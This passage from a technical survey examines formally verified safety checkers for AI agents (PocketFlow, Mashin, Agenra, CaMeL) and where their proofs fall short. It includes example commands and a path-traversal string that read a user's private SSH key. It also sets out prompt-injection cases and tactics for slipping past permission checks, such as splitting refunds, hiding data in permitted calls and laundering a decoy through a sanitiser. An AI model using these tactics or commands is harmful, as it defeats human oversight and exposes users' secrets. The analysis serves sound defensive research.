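&\text{(A1)}\quad \Pi_M(s_i,a_i,e_i,s_{i+1})\ \text{ at every step of every run of } M,\ \text{for every sequence of actions}\\
&\text{(A2)}\quad I \text{ refines } M\\
&\text{Conclusion:}\quad \Pi_I(t_i,a_i,f_i,t_{i+1})\ \text{ at every step of every run of } I,\ \text{for every model}
\end{aligned}
$$

Here t and f are the states and events of I. Refinement means three things.

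1. The starting states of the two machines match.
2. If two states match and I takes a step on some action, M can take a step on the same action, with a matching event and a matching new state.
3. If M's step obeys Π_M, the matching step of I obeys Π_I.

For any run of I, the proof builds a run of M with the same actions, using the second condition to add each new step. M's run obeys the policy throughout by A1, so I's run does too by the third condition. The proof doesn't depend on the reasons for the model's choices. The problem that refinement causes for noninterference doesn't arise here, because Π concerns one run at a time.

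Dafny checks both assumptions for PocketFlow, but the conclusion covers only events inside a formal machine. A corollary extends it to the real world: if every externally visible effect of the deployed system corresponds to an event of I, then every such effect obeys Π_I. Moon and Varshney call this condition *effect exclusivity*, and nobody has proved it. A developer could break it with a single node that opens a file directly in Python. It also fails if the code that carries out an event does something other than what the event represents, or if the agent finds a flaw in the Python runtime.

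Moon and Varshney therefore recommend running the loop inside a sandbox. They rank sandboxes below their own method because people audit sandboxes instead of proving them correct. That is true of Docker and similar products, but Moon and Varshney overlook seL4 and SeKVM, whose isolation theorems could prove much of what the corollary assumes.

Dafny's compiler translates the verified loop into Python, and Moon and Varshney deploy that translation. Someone who installs the ordinary PocketFlow package gets no guarantee from the proof. Users of the translated version still have to trust Dafny's verifier and compiler, the policy, and the definitions that match the two machines.

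### One permitted read and one forbidden one

Under PocketFlow's policy, the agent may read files only under a configured workspace folder, may call only listed tools, and must stop after a fixed number of steps. Suppose the folder is `/work/trip`, the only listed tool is `search_flights`, and the limit is 20 steps. After three steps, the model outputs a request to read a file.

| | Permitted action | Forbidden action |
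|---|---|---|
| Model's choice | Read `/work/trip/notes.txt` | Read `/home/ana/.ssh/id_rsa`, a private key |
| Result of the check | The path is under the folder | The path is outside the folder |
| Event | A read of that path | No effect |
| Recorded reads | One more entry | Unchanged |

If every recorded path is under the folder before either action, the same is true afterward. The list starts empty, so by induction the rule holds for as long as the agent runs. Repeating the forbidden request or inventing a good reason for it doesn't change the result, because the loop checks only the path.

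Even if every action is checked, a flawed rule can let a harmful one through. The Dafny lemma expresses the first rule as `StartsWith(path, workspace_root)`. If this function compares text, as its name suggests, it would accept `/work/trip/../../home/ana/.ssh/id_rsa`, which begins with the right characters. Each `..` means "go up one folder", so an operating system would open Ana's private key. Dafny would accept the proof whether or not the code has this flaw. A developer can resolve such paths before the check, but the code that does so would then belong to the trusted computing base.

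The tool rule checks only which tool the model calls. If the notes contain a passport number, the model can read them and then put the number into a flight search, because both actions are permitted. The general theorem allows rules about a tool's arguments, but this policy has none. A rule that forbade passport numbers in searches would still have to detect one that the model had disguised.

### Four runs and an empty clause

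Claude models wrote the formal specification and the proofs. Sonnet 4.6 explored the code, and Opus 4.7 did most of the writing. A specification written by a model with access to the code can be worthless, because the model may just describe what the code does, and the code will always satisfy that description. To prevent this, Moon and Varshney use an *information barrier*. The step that derives the safety property receives the interface and a trusted template, but not the implementation. A later step receives the code and builds a formal model of it, but can't change the property.

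Each specification then has to pass three gates before the final proof attempt:

- Dafny must be able to parse and type-check it within thirty seconds.
- Verification must fail after a program strips the invariant down to almost nothing and empties the proofs of the lemmas. If it still succeeds, the specification demands too little.
- Verification must also fail after a language model plants a plausible mistake in the proof file.

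Moon and Varshney tested this on two agents, one that reads files and one that retrieves documents to answer questions, in four runs with and without the barrier. Every specification passed the gates, and Dafny accepted every final proof. Checking each path through the graph took 1.2 to 2.5 seconds. A run used 1.6 to 3.4 million tokens, and removing the barrier raised token use by 25% to 56% because the model then also read the code repository. These time and token requirements are within reach of a small team, although the loop is far smaller than seL4.

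One accepted specification had a serious gap. The retrieval agent is supposed to read only documents on an approved list, but the template has no field for documents. The closest thing the template has is a rule about tools.

$$
\text{for every } j<|\mathit{tool\_calls}|:\quad \mathit{tool\_calls}[j]\in\mathit{allowed\_tools}
$$

Without the barrier, Opus had access to the agent's code, which had no list of tool calls, so it wrote a specification in which `tool_calls` stays empty. The rule is then true because it has nothing to apply to, and even an agent that read every document in the archive would satisfy it.

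With the barrier, Opus had no code to consult and used `tool_calls` to represent the documents. The resulting rule restricts which documents the agent may read, but a human reviewer has to know that "tool" means "document".

The gates missed the empty rule because they damage the proof as a whole and check that something fails. Other parts of the proof, such as the bookkeeping of the agent's history, failed as they should, and no gate tested the safety rules one at a time. The AI agents that verified xv6 produced a similar error, a crash-recovery theorem that assumed there was nothing to recover. Moon and Varshney propose checking that each rule applies to something in at least one reachable state. A stricter test would require, for each rule, an action that it rejects, and the empty rule would fail this test because it rejects nothing.

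### Better models and wider actions

Moon and Varshney claim that their guarantee doesn't weaken as models become more capable. This is true of the theorem, because it assumes nothing about the model. By contrast, a monitor that reads a model's written reasoning works only if that reasoning reflects what the model is doing, and safety training works only if its effects persist in deployment. Moon and Varshney cite experiments in which both conditions failed.

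The corollary is more vulnerable because it depends on the Python runtime, the operating system and every other route to the outside world, and more capable models are better at finding flaws in all of these. Moon and Varshney reply that engineers can find and repair a mismatch between a specification and a running program, whatever the model's abilities. But an agent may find the mismatch first. OpenAI's internal models found three ways to prove `False` in Lean, whose kernel has had far more scrutiny than most code around an agent.

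A better model can also do more with permitted actions. Hiding a passport number in a flight search takes some skill, as does choosing twenty steps that together achieve something nobody would have approved. The worst possible outcome may therefore become worse even though the policy allows the same events.

The choice of actions can matter even more than the model. Suppose a developer adds a tool called `shell`, which runs any command, and puts it on the list. The model calls it with this command:

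```
cat /home/ana/.ssh/id_rsa
```

The loop finds `shell` on the list and emits a tool event. The rule about the workspace folder also holds, because it covers only read events and there were none. Dafny accepts the same proof as before, even though the model now has the private key.

If reading the key counts as an effect of its own, no event represents it, so effect exclusivity fails and the corollary doesn't apply. If the tool event represents everything the command did, the corollary applies, but the policy permits anything a command can do. Either way, only the shell's own restrictions protect the key. Moon and Varshney acknowledge that a generic shell "collapses the guarantee onto the primitive", and they want framework developers to offer narrow actions instead.

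This is awkward for coding agents, which are useful largely because they can run commands. Actions that seem much safer than a shell can also permit more than they appear to. For example, an agent that can edit the tests and run the test suite can run any command by putting it in a test. To prevent this, the developer would have to restrict what the tests can do or who can change them. Moon and Varshney have verified an interface with four variants so far, and leave frameworks with dozens to future work.

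### Mashin's check-then-act operator

A Mashin program has no instruction for acting on the world. It can only issue a *directive*, a request to the runtime. The fourteen kinds of directive include calls to a language model, web requests, file operations and shell commands. Inside the formal model, this gives Mashin the equivalent of effect exclusivity, because nobody can write a program that acts directly. For the deployed system, McCann lists the absence of hidden effects as an assumption.

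McCann represents programs as *interaction trees*. Each node is a final result, a silent step, or an event with one branch for every possible reply. A call to a language model is an event. The proof has to cover every branch, so it holds whatever the model replies, as in PocketFlow.

A *handler* is the code that carries out directives. McCann's governance operator wraps a handler in checks, and for each directive it does the following:

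```
check trust, permission, phase and pre-hooks
if every check passes:
    carry out the directive
    run guardrails, record provenance, broadcast
    return the result
otherwise:
    loop forever
```

A refused directive has no effect because the program enters an endless loop instead of carrying it out. *Effect-Transparent Governance for AI Workflow Architectures* (McCann, 2026) describes this as giving up liveness for safety, meaning that the program may never finish but will not perform an unauthorised action. An assistant that asks to send one forbidden email would never do anything again. The deployed runtime uses a timeout to detect such refusals. In systems where stopping is dangerous, an endless loop would be the wrong response.

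The guardrails run after the handler has carried out the directive, so they can't prevent its effects. The operator as printed also discards whatever this last group of steps returns.

*Effect-Transparent Governance* also proves that when every check passes, a program wrapped in the operator produces the same result as it would without the checks.

### A flag that stays up after a refusal

The main safety theorem uses a predicate called `gov_safe`, which goes through a tree with a true-or-false flag. Its rules, as printed in the April paper, are as follows.

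| Next node in the tree | When `gov_safe` accepts it |
|---|---|
| Final result | Always |
| Silent step | The rest is safe with the same flag |
| Check | For both possible answers, the rest is safe with the flag set to true |
| Effect on the world | The flag is true, and the rest is safe with the flag still true |

McCann proved that for every handler and every program, the wrapped program satisfies `gov_safe`, whether the flag starts true or false. The predicate is not trivial, because a program that acts before any check, with the flag false, fails it.

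However, consider a program that asks for permission to send an email and sends it regardless of the answer.

1. The flag is false at the start.
2. The program performs a check, and the answer is no. The third rule still sets the flag to true.
3. The program sends the email. The flag is true, so the fourth rule accepts this.
4. The program ends, which is always safe.

`gov_safe` therefore accepts a program that ignores a refusal. It also accepts one that performs a single check and then sends a million emails, because no rule resets the flag to false.

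This doesn't look like a printing error. The Rocq code in the April paper requires the flag to be true for both answers, and the accompanying proof applies the rule that way. *Effect-Transparent Governance* also describes governance events as granting permission, without mentioning their answers.

The theorem is therefore too weak to distinguish Mashin's operator from one that never blocks anything. If someone removed the "if" from the operator, it would run all four checks and then carry out the directive regardless of the results. The altered operator would still satisfy the safety theorem. It would also satisfy the theorem about unchanged results, because the two operators behave identically when every check passes.

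*Algebraic Semantics of Governed Execution* (McCann, 2026) turns these two properties into axioms that any governance operator should satisfy. A third axiom requires equivalent handlers to remain equivalent after wrapping. The altered operator satisfies all three axioms with the April version of `gov_safe`.

Mashin's real operator does block refused directives, which a reader can confirm from its few lines of code. McCann also proved, in a separate theorem, that a denied directive produces no input or output in a specification of the runtime's interpreter. So the design has the property users want, but the headline theorem doesn't prove it.

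*Algebraic Semantics* also prints a stricter version of `gov_safe`, in which each check sets the flag to its own answer and each effect sets it back to false. This version rejects the program that ignores a refusal, but it is too strict for the theorem printed beside it, which covers every handler. A handler may need two effects for one approved directive, such as opening a connection and then sending the message. The first effect sets the flag to false, so the second is unsafe. The April proof explicitly allows handlers with several effects and relies on the flag staying true between them. Rocq therefore probably checked the weaker version.

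A version between the two would fit the operator better. If each check set the flag to its result and effects didn't change the flag, the program that ignores a refusal would fail. Mashin's operator would pass with any handler, because after a refusal it only loops. One approval could still cover several actions. In the formal tree, a check includes the name of its stage, such as "permission", but not the directive under review, so the predicate can't match approvals to actions.

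The theorem also does not connect a directive to what the handler does. It holds for every handler, including one that responds to an approved request to read a note by deleting it. The check is therefore useful only if the handler does what the program asked for.

*Intent-Driven Computing* (McCann, 2026) states a theorem closer to what one would want: an effect can occur only if the runtime has returned "allow" for that request and recorded the decision. The theorem is about a separate, small language with a handful of rules. Only one of these rules can produce an effect, so the proof follows almost directly from the rules. McCann cites a Rocq file for the theorem, `GovernanceMediation.v`, which isn't in the April paper's list of files.

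### From the proofs to the running system

According to the April paper, the Rocq development contains 454 theorems in 36 files, with no gaps in the proofs. But the paper's own subtotals add up to 548, and mashin-live, the company's page on a code-sharing site, also gives 548, in 32 files. The discrepancy doesn't make any theorem false, and even an accurate count would be a poor guide to the strength of the work, because McCann classifies only 30 of the results as core and 102 as scaffolding. McCann writes that if Rocq accepts the development, every theorem in it is correct. That is true if Rocq is sound, but a correct theorem can still prove less than its name suggests, as `gov_safe` does.

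Mashin runs on BEAM, the virtual machine built for the language Erlang. Rocq translates part of the development into OCaml, and Mashin loads the result into BEAM as a native library. The translated functions decide whether a program's trust level and capabilities permit a directive. The operator that makes every directive wait for this decision isn't translated, so unverified runtime code must call the decision function each time and follow the result, as a Keleusma host must with its kernel. If the native library is unavailable, Mashin falls back on an unverified version written in Elixir, another language for BEAM.

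To check whether the runtime matches the specification, McCann wrote a 148-line interpreter that closely follows the Rocq version and compared it with the runtime. The tests cover seven properties, with 10,000 random inputs each. Among other things, they check that the interpreter and the runtime permit and refuse the same directives, that raising the trust level never removes a permission, and that a refused directive halts the rest of the sequence.

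The 188th input exposed a bug. It contained a directive to run a shell command, which the specification permitted but the runtime refused. The runtime's interpreter looked for a capability called `compute.exec`, but the runtime's table of capabilities had only `compute.code.execute`. Each part worked on its own, so ordinary unit tests had missed it. After McCann added the missing name, the comparison ran on more than 70,000 inputs without a disagreement.

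This mistake did not weaken security, because the runtime blocked a command it should have allowed. A mismatch between two names could just as easily have made the runtime allow a command it should have blocked, and the same tests would have had a good chance of catching that.

The April paper is inconsistent about what these tests cover. Its testing section describes a comparison with the BEAM runtime, but its limitations section describes a comparison with a reference interpreter and not with the runtime directly. The bug was in the runtime's own table, so the tests must have reached at least that table.

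Ten thousand random inputs without a disagreement are good evidence about random inputs. By a standard statistical rule, they give 95% confidence that the two sides disagree on fewer than about 3 in 10,000 inputs drawn the same way. A hostile program wouldn't draw its inputs at random. Fortunately, the permission decision is small enough to test completely. With 14 kinds of directive, 6 trust levels and 8 capabilities that a program may or may not declare, the number of cases is

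$$
14\times 6\times 2^8 = 21{,}504.
$$

*Algebraic Semantics* reports such a comparison between the translated library and the Elixir code, covering every combination of trust level and capability. For this part of Mashin, that is stronger evidence than the tests on 70,000 random inputs.

The checks take very little time compared with a language model's reply. In the April paper, the median time over 50 runs was 0.23 milliseconds with the checks and 0.24 without, so any difference was smaller than the normal variation between runs. *Intent-Driven Computing* reports about 0.54 milliseconds for each decision, nearly all of it spent writing the record to disk.

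### What each theorem guarantees

The four questions asked of the email kernel bring out how little the two theorems overlap.

| Question | PocketFlow | Mashin |
|---|---|---|
| What is the theorem? | Every event obeys the rules on paths, tools and steps | Every effect comes after at least one check, whatever the answer |
| Which inputs does it cover? | Every sequence of typed actions | Every program, every model reply and every handler |
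| What must the other software do? | Send every effect through the loop, and carry out exactly the event that the loop emits | Wrap every directive, answer the checks sensibly, and carry out what the program requested |
| What is unconstrained after release? | The contents of files, and what the agent tells a permitted tool | The results of directives, and what later directives do with them |

PocketFlow's theorem is stronger for most purposes because it includes the policy. In Mashin's main theorem, the answers to the checks come from outside the tree and may be anything. A separate part of the Rocq development specifies when to grant permission, based only on the kind of directive, the trust level and the declared capabilities. Under these rules, an untrusted program can't make a web request, while a program with the right capability can send one to any address. PocketFlow's rule about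 folders, by contrast, depends on where each file is.

*Intent-Driven Computing* describes more detailed policies, using the example of a simulated agent that handles customer refunds. For 200 requests, the agent proposed 847 actions. The runtime allowed 423, denied 312, and referred the other 112 to a person. McCann then replayed the record with a refund limit of $1,000 instead of $500 and found that 89 of the denied actions would have passed. This is a useful way to try out a policy, though it assumes the agent would have proposed the same later actions after receiving a different answer.

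A limit on each refund leaves an obvious way around it. The agent can turn a forbidden $900 refund into two refunds of $450. McCann acknowledges that a harmful plan may consist entirely of authorised actions. A policy that remembers earlier refunds can stop this one:

$$
\text{total already refunded to the customer}+\text{new refund}\le 500
$$

This is still a safety property, and PocketFlow's theorem would allow it, since Π may refer to the state. But a person has to think of the rule first, and an agent can divide up a plan in many other ways.

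### Why truthfulness is outside both theorems

Moon and Varshney exclude truthfulness and deception from their guarantee, and McCann excludes the factual correctness of what a model writes. A longer proof couldn't remove either exclusion, for much the same reason that Lean can't prove when a bridge opened. Suppose an agent tells a user "The bridge opened in 1932" in two worlds that differ only in the year the bridge opened. The agent's software is in the same state in both, so a proof about the software can't establish whether the statement is true.

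$$
\begin{array}{lcc}
 & \text{opened in 1932} & \text{opened in 1933}\\
\Pi(s,a,e,s') & \text{same value} & \text{same value}\\
\text{message is true} & \text{yes} & \text{no}
\end{array}
$$

Π depends only on s, a, e and s′, so it must accept the message in both worlds or reject it in both. No policy of this form can therefore accept every true message and reject every false one. Mashin's checks have the same limit because they also depend only on the information available to the software.

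McCann offers a different explanation, based on Rice's theorem, which shows that no algorithm can decide for every program whether its behaviour has a given non-trivial property. McCann infers that no ordinary program could replace the opaque component, in practice a language model, for all tasks that need judgement. This doesn't follow, because a limit on what we can decide about programs in general doesn't stop a particular program from answering well, and McCann acknowledges that language models are themselves computable. We don't need the theorem to explain the bridge example, because the policy simply lacks the relevant fact.

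As with Lean, a policy could at best require the agent's answer to match an archive of opening dates. That check would be much easier to write if `Action` had a variant for stating a bridge's opening date, with fields for the bridge and the year, than if the agent could send any text.

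## Agenra: a verified permission checker for agents

A limit on a customer's total refunds works only if the checker keeps a record of earlier refunds. *AgentFlow* (Shivakumar, Priya and Gao, 2026) describes a checker that keeps such records for every tool an agent uses. The August 2026 draft called the system AgentFlow, and an October revision renames it Agenra. Each permission has a quota, and each use subtracts one unit from it. *A Linear Logic of Authorization and Knowledge*, by Garg, Bauer and colleagues, had earlier built a logic for such "consumable authorizations" on linear logic, where using an assumption normally uses it up.

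Agenra's permission checker is written in Lean, which is both a proof assistant and a programming language, so the code that runs is the same code the theorems are about. A Python layer translates the policy, forwards each call the agent proposes to a Lean process, and runs the tool only if the answer is "allow". The Lean process also keeps the labels, the history and the remaining quotas, whereas Mashin's verified code only checks whether a directive is permissible.

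### Sending one report to Alice

In the main example, a user wants the public fields of a private report emailed to Alice, at most once. The agent has six tools. `Read` fetches the report, `Sanitize` reduces it to its public fields, `Lookup` gets Alice's entry from a directory, `Extract` takes the address from that entry, and `Send` sends the email. `Other` reads unrelated, untrusted content. The user and the application each grant one use of each tool, and every call needs a grant from both.

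Agenra stores each result and gives the agent a *handle*, which is a reference to the stored value. The agent builds its next call from handles instead of typing the email itself. For each value, Lean records a label and the tool that produced it.

| Call | Stored value | Secrecy label | Producer |
|---|---|---|---|
| `Read` | The whole report | Confidential | `Read` |
| `Sanitize`, on the report | Its public fields | Public | `Sanitize` |
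| `Lookup` | Alice's directory entry | Public | `Lookup` |
| `Extract`, on the entry | Alice's address | Public | `Extract` |

The agent can make these calls in six orders, since it only has to read the report before sanitising it and look up the entry before extracting the address. It then proposes a `Send` with the public fields as the body and the address as the recipient. Lean checks five things.

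1. *Approval.* A reviewer must have approved this exact call, with these two stored values, and the approval must be unused.
2. *Recipient.* The policy doesn't contain Alice's address. It has an empty slot that only the designated `Lookup` can fill, and the proposed recipient must equal the address in the slot.
3. *Quota.* Both lists must have a send left. Lean sets aside one unit on each.
4. *Label.* Lean joins the labels of the body and the recipient, keeping the stricter one. The result must be Public.
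5. *Producer.* The body must have come from `Sanitize`.

If the agent uses the whole report as the body, the joined label is Confidential and Lean rejects the message. An address from a malicious web page fails the recipient check because `Other` can't fill the slot. If a repeated lookup returns a different address, the slot closes for the rest of the task, so the report can't be sent to anyone.

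When every check passes, Lean deducts the two units and marks the approval as used, and only then does Python call the mail server. If the server reports an error, Lean restores neither, because a server can deliver a message and lose the connection before confirming it. Restoring them after every error would let the agent send the report twice. As a result, a server outage at this point ends the task, and somebody has to start a new one.

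Shivakumar and colleagues prove, partly in Lean and partly by hand, that every `Send` that reaches the mail tool has passed all five checks, and that at most one `Send` per task reaches it, counting any that fail. The proof covers any sequence of calls the agent might propose, as long as Agenra handles them one at a time. It doesn't establish noninterference, and it doesn't cover timing or what Alice does with the email.

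### A decoy that passes every check

The original policy did not check what produced the body. It accepted any Public value, so the agent could have sent Alice the text from `Other` as if it were the report. The later policy adds what Shivakumar and colleagues call an origin rule, which requires the body to come from `Sanitize`.

The agent can still get around that rule by running the text from `Other` through `Sanitize` and sending the result. The output is Public, its producer is `Sanitize`, and the recipient and quota checks pass, so Lean allows the send and Alice receives a decoy. The policy declares that `Sanitize` releases report 42, but that phrase is the same whatever record the tool receives. To stop the decoy, a person has to write another origin rule, requiring the input of `Sanitize` to come from `Read`.

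Lean works correctly throughout. The theorem about origins guarantees that the body has the producer the policy names, and the decoy has that producer. The labels contained enough information to catch the decoy, because they also record whether a value came from a trusted source, and `Sanitize` as printed changes only the secrecy part. But the rule for `Send` doesn't include a trust check.

The guarantee in *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (David, Guarnieri and Gervais, 2026) also excludes errors in writing the policy. The paper's monitor polices agents that test websites for security holes. One client's brief allows tests on "all subdomains" of its site, and somebody has to decide whether that includes a subdomain that leads to another company's servers. Lean checks the theorems about the monitor, but not whether the policy matches what the client meant.

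### What the proofs take on trust

Several parts of the report example belong to the trusted computing base although nobody has verified them.

| Part | What it must do | What can happen if it fails |
|---|---|---|
| Python layer | Translate the policy correctly, and run exactly the call that Lean checked | Lean approves one email and Python sends another |
| `Sanitize` | Remove every private field | A secret leaves with a Public label |
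| Directory | Return Alice's real address | A stranger gets the report |
| Reviewer | Understand the call before approving it | The approval adds no protection |
| Tool declarations | List everything a tool does | An agent deletes a file without a permission for it |

The last failure occurred in a test. Shivakumar and colleagues registered a batch tool with fewer effects than it had, and Lean allowed an undeclared deletion.

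Lean runs in its own process, so a memory error in Python can't corrupt it, but Python can still call the mail server directly. An agent framework that logs Lean's refusal as an error and then runs the tool anyway would break complete mediation, just as a Keleusma host would by ignoring its kernel.

Of these parts, the secrecy argument depends most on `Sanitize`. A Lean proof shows that, if the labels are right and Agenra knows every input of every tool, no Public email derives from a Confidential value except through a trusted release, which here is `Sanitize`. For three fixed fields of a database record, a programmer can write `Sanitize` in a few lines and check it by eye. If it were a language model asked to "remove anything sensitive", the theorem would still hold, but the assumption behind it would be much harder to defend.

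### How much a reviewer's approval is worth

Each Agenra approval covers one operation on particular stored values, so identical text under a new handle needs a new approval. An approval doesn't change the labels, so a reviewer can't approve the whole report at once. Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Temporary Authority, Permanent Effects*, argues that an approval should still be fresh when the action takes effect, and should apply to that same effect. Agenra enforces the second requirement strictly but does less about freshness, since an unused approval stays valid during the task even if the reviewer's reasons for it no longer hold.

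None of this helps if the reviewer isn't paying attention. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports an experiment in which 1,053 paid testers each saw one permission prompt replaced by a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% refused it. The refusal rate fell from about 17% early in a session to 5% after fifty or more prompts. Anthropic published these figures to support an automatic classifier that blocked 89% of the same commands, and the testers had less to lose because they were not working on their own projects. Still, the practitioners in *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026) described clicking through familiar prompts and taking less care over time.

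Better prompts seem to help somewhat. Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, give the example of a user who wants an auditor to receive only summary totals. Hidden instructions in a vendor's note lead the agent to copy the raw invoices into `report.csv` and then ask to send that file to the auditor. The tool, the recipient and the file name all look fine. The 80 volunteers in their study approved 55.0% of unsafe requests when they saw a plain prompt, 32.5% when they also saw the user's original instructions and a full log, and 24.2% when they were also shown the combined consequence. The last improvement could be chance, since the 95% interval for the difference runs from a drop of 19.7 points to a rise of 3.8.

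Agenra requires one approval per report, which is much better than dozens of prompts an hour. The label check would also have caught the invoices, but only if someone had labelled them Confidential.

### Two deletions

When permissions can run out, giving an agent more permission can stop it from finishing its work. Ordinary access lists don't have this problem.

Suppose permission 1 lets an agent delete file B once, and permission 2 lets it delete file A once. Lean goes through the list in order and deducts one use from the first permission that matches and has any left. The administrator then widens permission 1 to cover file A as well.

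| Permission | Before | After |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Delete B, once | Delete A or B, once |
| 2 | Delete A, once | Delete A, once |

The agent's task is to delete A and then B. Before the change, A uses permission 2 and B uses permission 1. Afterwards, A uses permission 1 because it now comes first, and no remaining permission covers B. If the agent asks for both deletions in a single call, Lean rejects the whole call.

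The change also lets the agent delete A twice, which the specification forbids and which was impossible before. The first deletion uses permission 1 and the second uses permission 2. An administrator could easily miss both effects, because the agent can still delete either file on its own and can still complete the task in the order B, then A.

A better charging method would fix this task, but no method can avoid the problem in general if it must charge each action immediately and can never change the charge. Suppose an agent has one permission for A or B and another for A or C, each good for one use. If the agent does A first, the checker must charge it before it's clear whether B or C will follow. If it charges A to the first permission, a later B fails, and if it charges A to the second, a later C fails. In *Managing Digital Rights using Linear Logic*, Barth and Mitchell (2006) proved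 a similar result for music players that must immediately choose which right in a licence to use up. Every such method will sometimes refuse a song that it allowed under a less flexible licence. They also give a method that can revise earlier charges, which Agenra never does, and prove that it avoids this problem.

### Preserving useful work

A change to a policy therefore raises two separate questions. Let Adm(P) be the set of tasks (sequences of calls and results) that the checker allows under permissions P.

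$$
\begin{aligned}
&\text{excluding harm:} && \mathrm{Adm}(P_{\text{new}})\ \text{contains no forbidden task}\\
&\text{preserving work:} && \mathrm{Adm}(P_{\text{old}})\subseteq \mathrm{Adm}(P_{\text{new}})
\end{aligned}
$$

A permission policy has to be judged on both the harm it excludes and the work it preserves, because a checker can exclude all harm by refusing everything or preserve all work by allowing everything. Shivakumar and colleagues tried several changes to the deletion policy on six legitimate tasks, and the results included every combination of harm excluded or allowed and work preserved or blocked.

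| Change | Legitimate tasks kept | Forbidden task possible |
|---|---|---|
| Reverse the two permissions | 6 of 6 | No |
| Add another permission for A | 6 of 6 | Yes |
| Remove the permission for A | 1 of 6 | No |
| Widen permission 1 to A or B | 4 of 6 | Yes |

Agenra can use a *simulation* to prove that a change preserves work. A simulation is a relation R between the old and new counters, which record how much of each permission the agent has used. R must satisfy two conditions.

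$$
\begin{aligned}
&(\text{old start},\ \text{new start})\in R\\
&\text{if }(s,s')\in R\text{ and the old policy allows } e \text{ in } s,\text{ leading to } t,\\
&\quad\text{then the new policy allows } e \text{ in } s',\text{ leading to some } t' \text{ with } (t,t')\in R
\end{aligned}
$$

By induction, the new policy can then follow the old one through a task of any length. PocketFlow's refinement proof has the same form but runs in the opposite direction, because it shows that the new machine does nothing extra, while this proof shows that the agent loses nothing.

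Adding another permission for A at the end of the list passes easily. The old counters (x, y) pair with the new counters (x, y, 0). Each deletion that the old policy allows counts against the same permission under the new one, so the extra permission's counter stays at 0 and the pairs still match.

The widened policy fails after two steps.

| Action | Old counters | New counters |
|---|---|---|
| Start | (0, 0) | (0, 0) |
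| Delete A | (0, 1) | (1, 0) |
| Delete B | (1, 1) | Refused |

R must contain the starting pair, so it must also contain the pair reached by deleting A. The old policy allows B from there and the new one doesn't, so no relation can meet both conditions.

Python searches for R and Lean checks it, just as proof checkers check the output of untrusted provers. For simple changes, such as a larger quota or a swap of two permissions that never cover the same action, Lean accepts a shorter argument. Either way, the guarantee applies to a new task that makes one call at a time, with the same tools and the same replies from services and reviewers.

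Agenra checks for harm in a separate analysis. It runs its Lean functions on every sequence of calls up to a chosen length, using recorded results in place of real tools, and looks for a forbidden sequence. It also looks for a sequence that completes the task, and reports "vacuous" if it finds neither. In the report example, the agent needs five calls and an approval to deliver the report legitimately, so a search limited to five events can't get that far. The "vacuous" verdict shows the developer that finding no harm in such a search means little. A similar warning would have helped with the empty rule in PocketFlow's specification.

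### The 51 revisions

Shivakumar and colleagues wrote 51 changes to small policies. Of these, 24 are the possible orderings of one four-permission policy, and the others add, remove or edit permissions. A separate program, with its own code for matching and charging, found that 21 of the changes preserve all earlier tasks. Agenra certified those 21 and none of the other 30. Sixteen of the certified changes needed only the shorter argument, and five needed a simulation.

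These two results deserve different weight. The theorem already implies that a change gets no preservation certificate if it blocks a task the old policy allowed. So the score of 0 out of 30 mainly tests whether the code around the theorem works, and one wrong certificate would have exposed a fault. No theorem implies that Agenra recognises every preserving change, and it can miss some. It checks a call's effects one by one, so it may reject a change because of a combination of counter values that no real call leaves behind. The score of 21 out of 21 therefore depends heavily on which changes the authors thought of, and they say that the set is not a representative sample.

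One change came from real software. Dyad, a tool for building apps with AI, raised its free allowance from five agent messages to ten (*Basic Agent free quota increased to 10 messages*). Agenra certified the increase. With two chats to choose between, all 63 possible sequences of up to five messages remain among the 2,047 sequences of up to ten. However, Dyad refunds failed messages and renews the allowance after a time, and Agenra's model does neither. Such limits also change often, and Dyad has since moved to 20 messages a day (*More free Basic Agent messages, build verification in Agent mode*).

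Raising a number is about the easiest change to certify. *FAVA* (2026) examined instruction files on GitHub that developers write for coding agents, and found that the permissions in them often depend on the state of the program and the order of earlier steps. Agenra can express some such rules, but nobody has yet measured how many real changes to them it could certify.

### Trials with agents, and the cost of checking

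The agent trials compared no guard, a simple hand-written guard, and Agenra. In the report task, fixed attacks got the language model Qwen to send the raw report in 15 of 20 unguarded runs, and the model Hermes in 1 of 20. With either guard, neither model ever sent it. The attacks disrupted the work with or without a guard. In each of the three set-ups, Qwen completed only 5 of 20 attacked tasks and Hermes completed 10 of 20.

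So the trials give no reason to prefer Agenra to the handwritten guard, and one result favours the guard. The trials used the original policy, which had no origin rule. When Shivakumar and colleagues replayed recorded calls, Agenra admitted five emails whose bodies had the wrong producer, while the handwritten guard admitted none. Agenra rejects all five under the later policy. Its advantage must come from maintenance, where it can check a changed policy against the old one.

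A further 378 runs with three configurations of Claude models didn't distinguish between the guards either. No attack in the GitHub tasks succeeded against any configuration, even without a guard. The August draft had reported a larger effect on AgentDojo, a public benchmark of agent tasks with planted instructions. The rate of confirmed compromise fell from 33.0% to 0.0% over 949 cases, and the share of tasks completed rose from 46.7% to 63.3%. The draft describes these results as preliminary.

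The checks take almost no time compared with a call to a language model. Checking a workflow of three to five calls took 1.3 to 3.0 milliseconds with the Lean checker, up to twice as long as with an equivalent in Python, and setting up each task took another 22 milliseconds. Certifying a change to a policy takes about a tenth of a second. The search for forbidden sequences takes the most time. For the report example, it took 0.8 seconds to cover every sequence of up to six events and 154 seconds for up to eight, so for now it suits only short tasks.

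## CaMeL and LLMBDA: keeping labels on values while an agent works

Agenra checks an agent's tool calls one at a time, but the agent chooses each call outside the checker, where text planted by an attacker may influence the choice. CaMeL brings the agent's plan inside the checker. A language model writes the plan as a program after reading only the user's request. An interpreter then runs the program and keeps a label on every value in it.

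CaMeL grew out of a pattern for agents that read untrusted text, which Willison (2023) proposed in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*. A *quarantined* model with no tools reads the text, and its answers go into variables. A *privileged* model uses the tools and can refer to the variables, but it never reads their contents or the text. Debenedetti and colleagues (2025) pointed out a gap in this pattern in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design*. If the quarantined model looks up an address in a tampered document, it may return the attacker's address, and the privileged model will use it. CaMeL's labels are meant to close this gap.

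### A request with a planted instruction

Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, explains the system with a user who wants to send Bob a reminder and whose last email contains Bob's address. The privileged model turns the request into a program much like this one:

```
mail    = get_last_email()
address = ask_quarantined("Find Bob's address", mail)
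send_email(to=address, body="Our meeting is tomorrow.")
```

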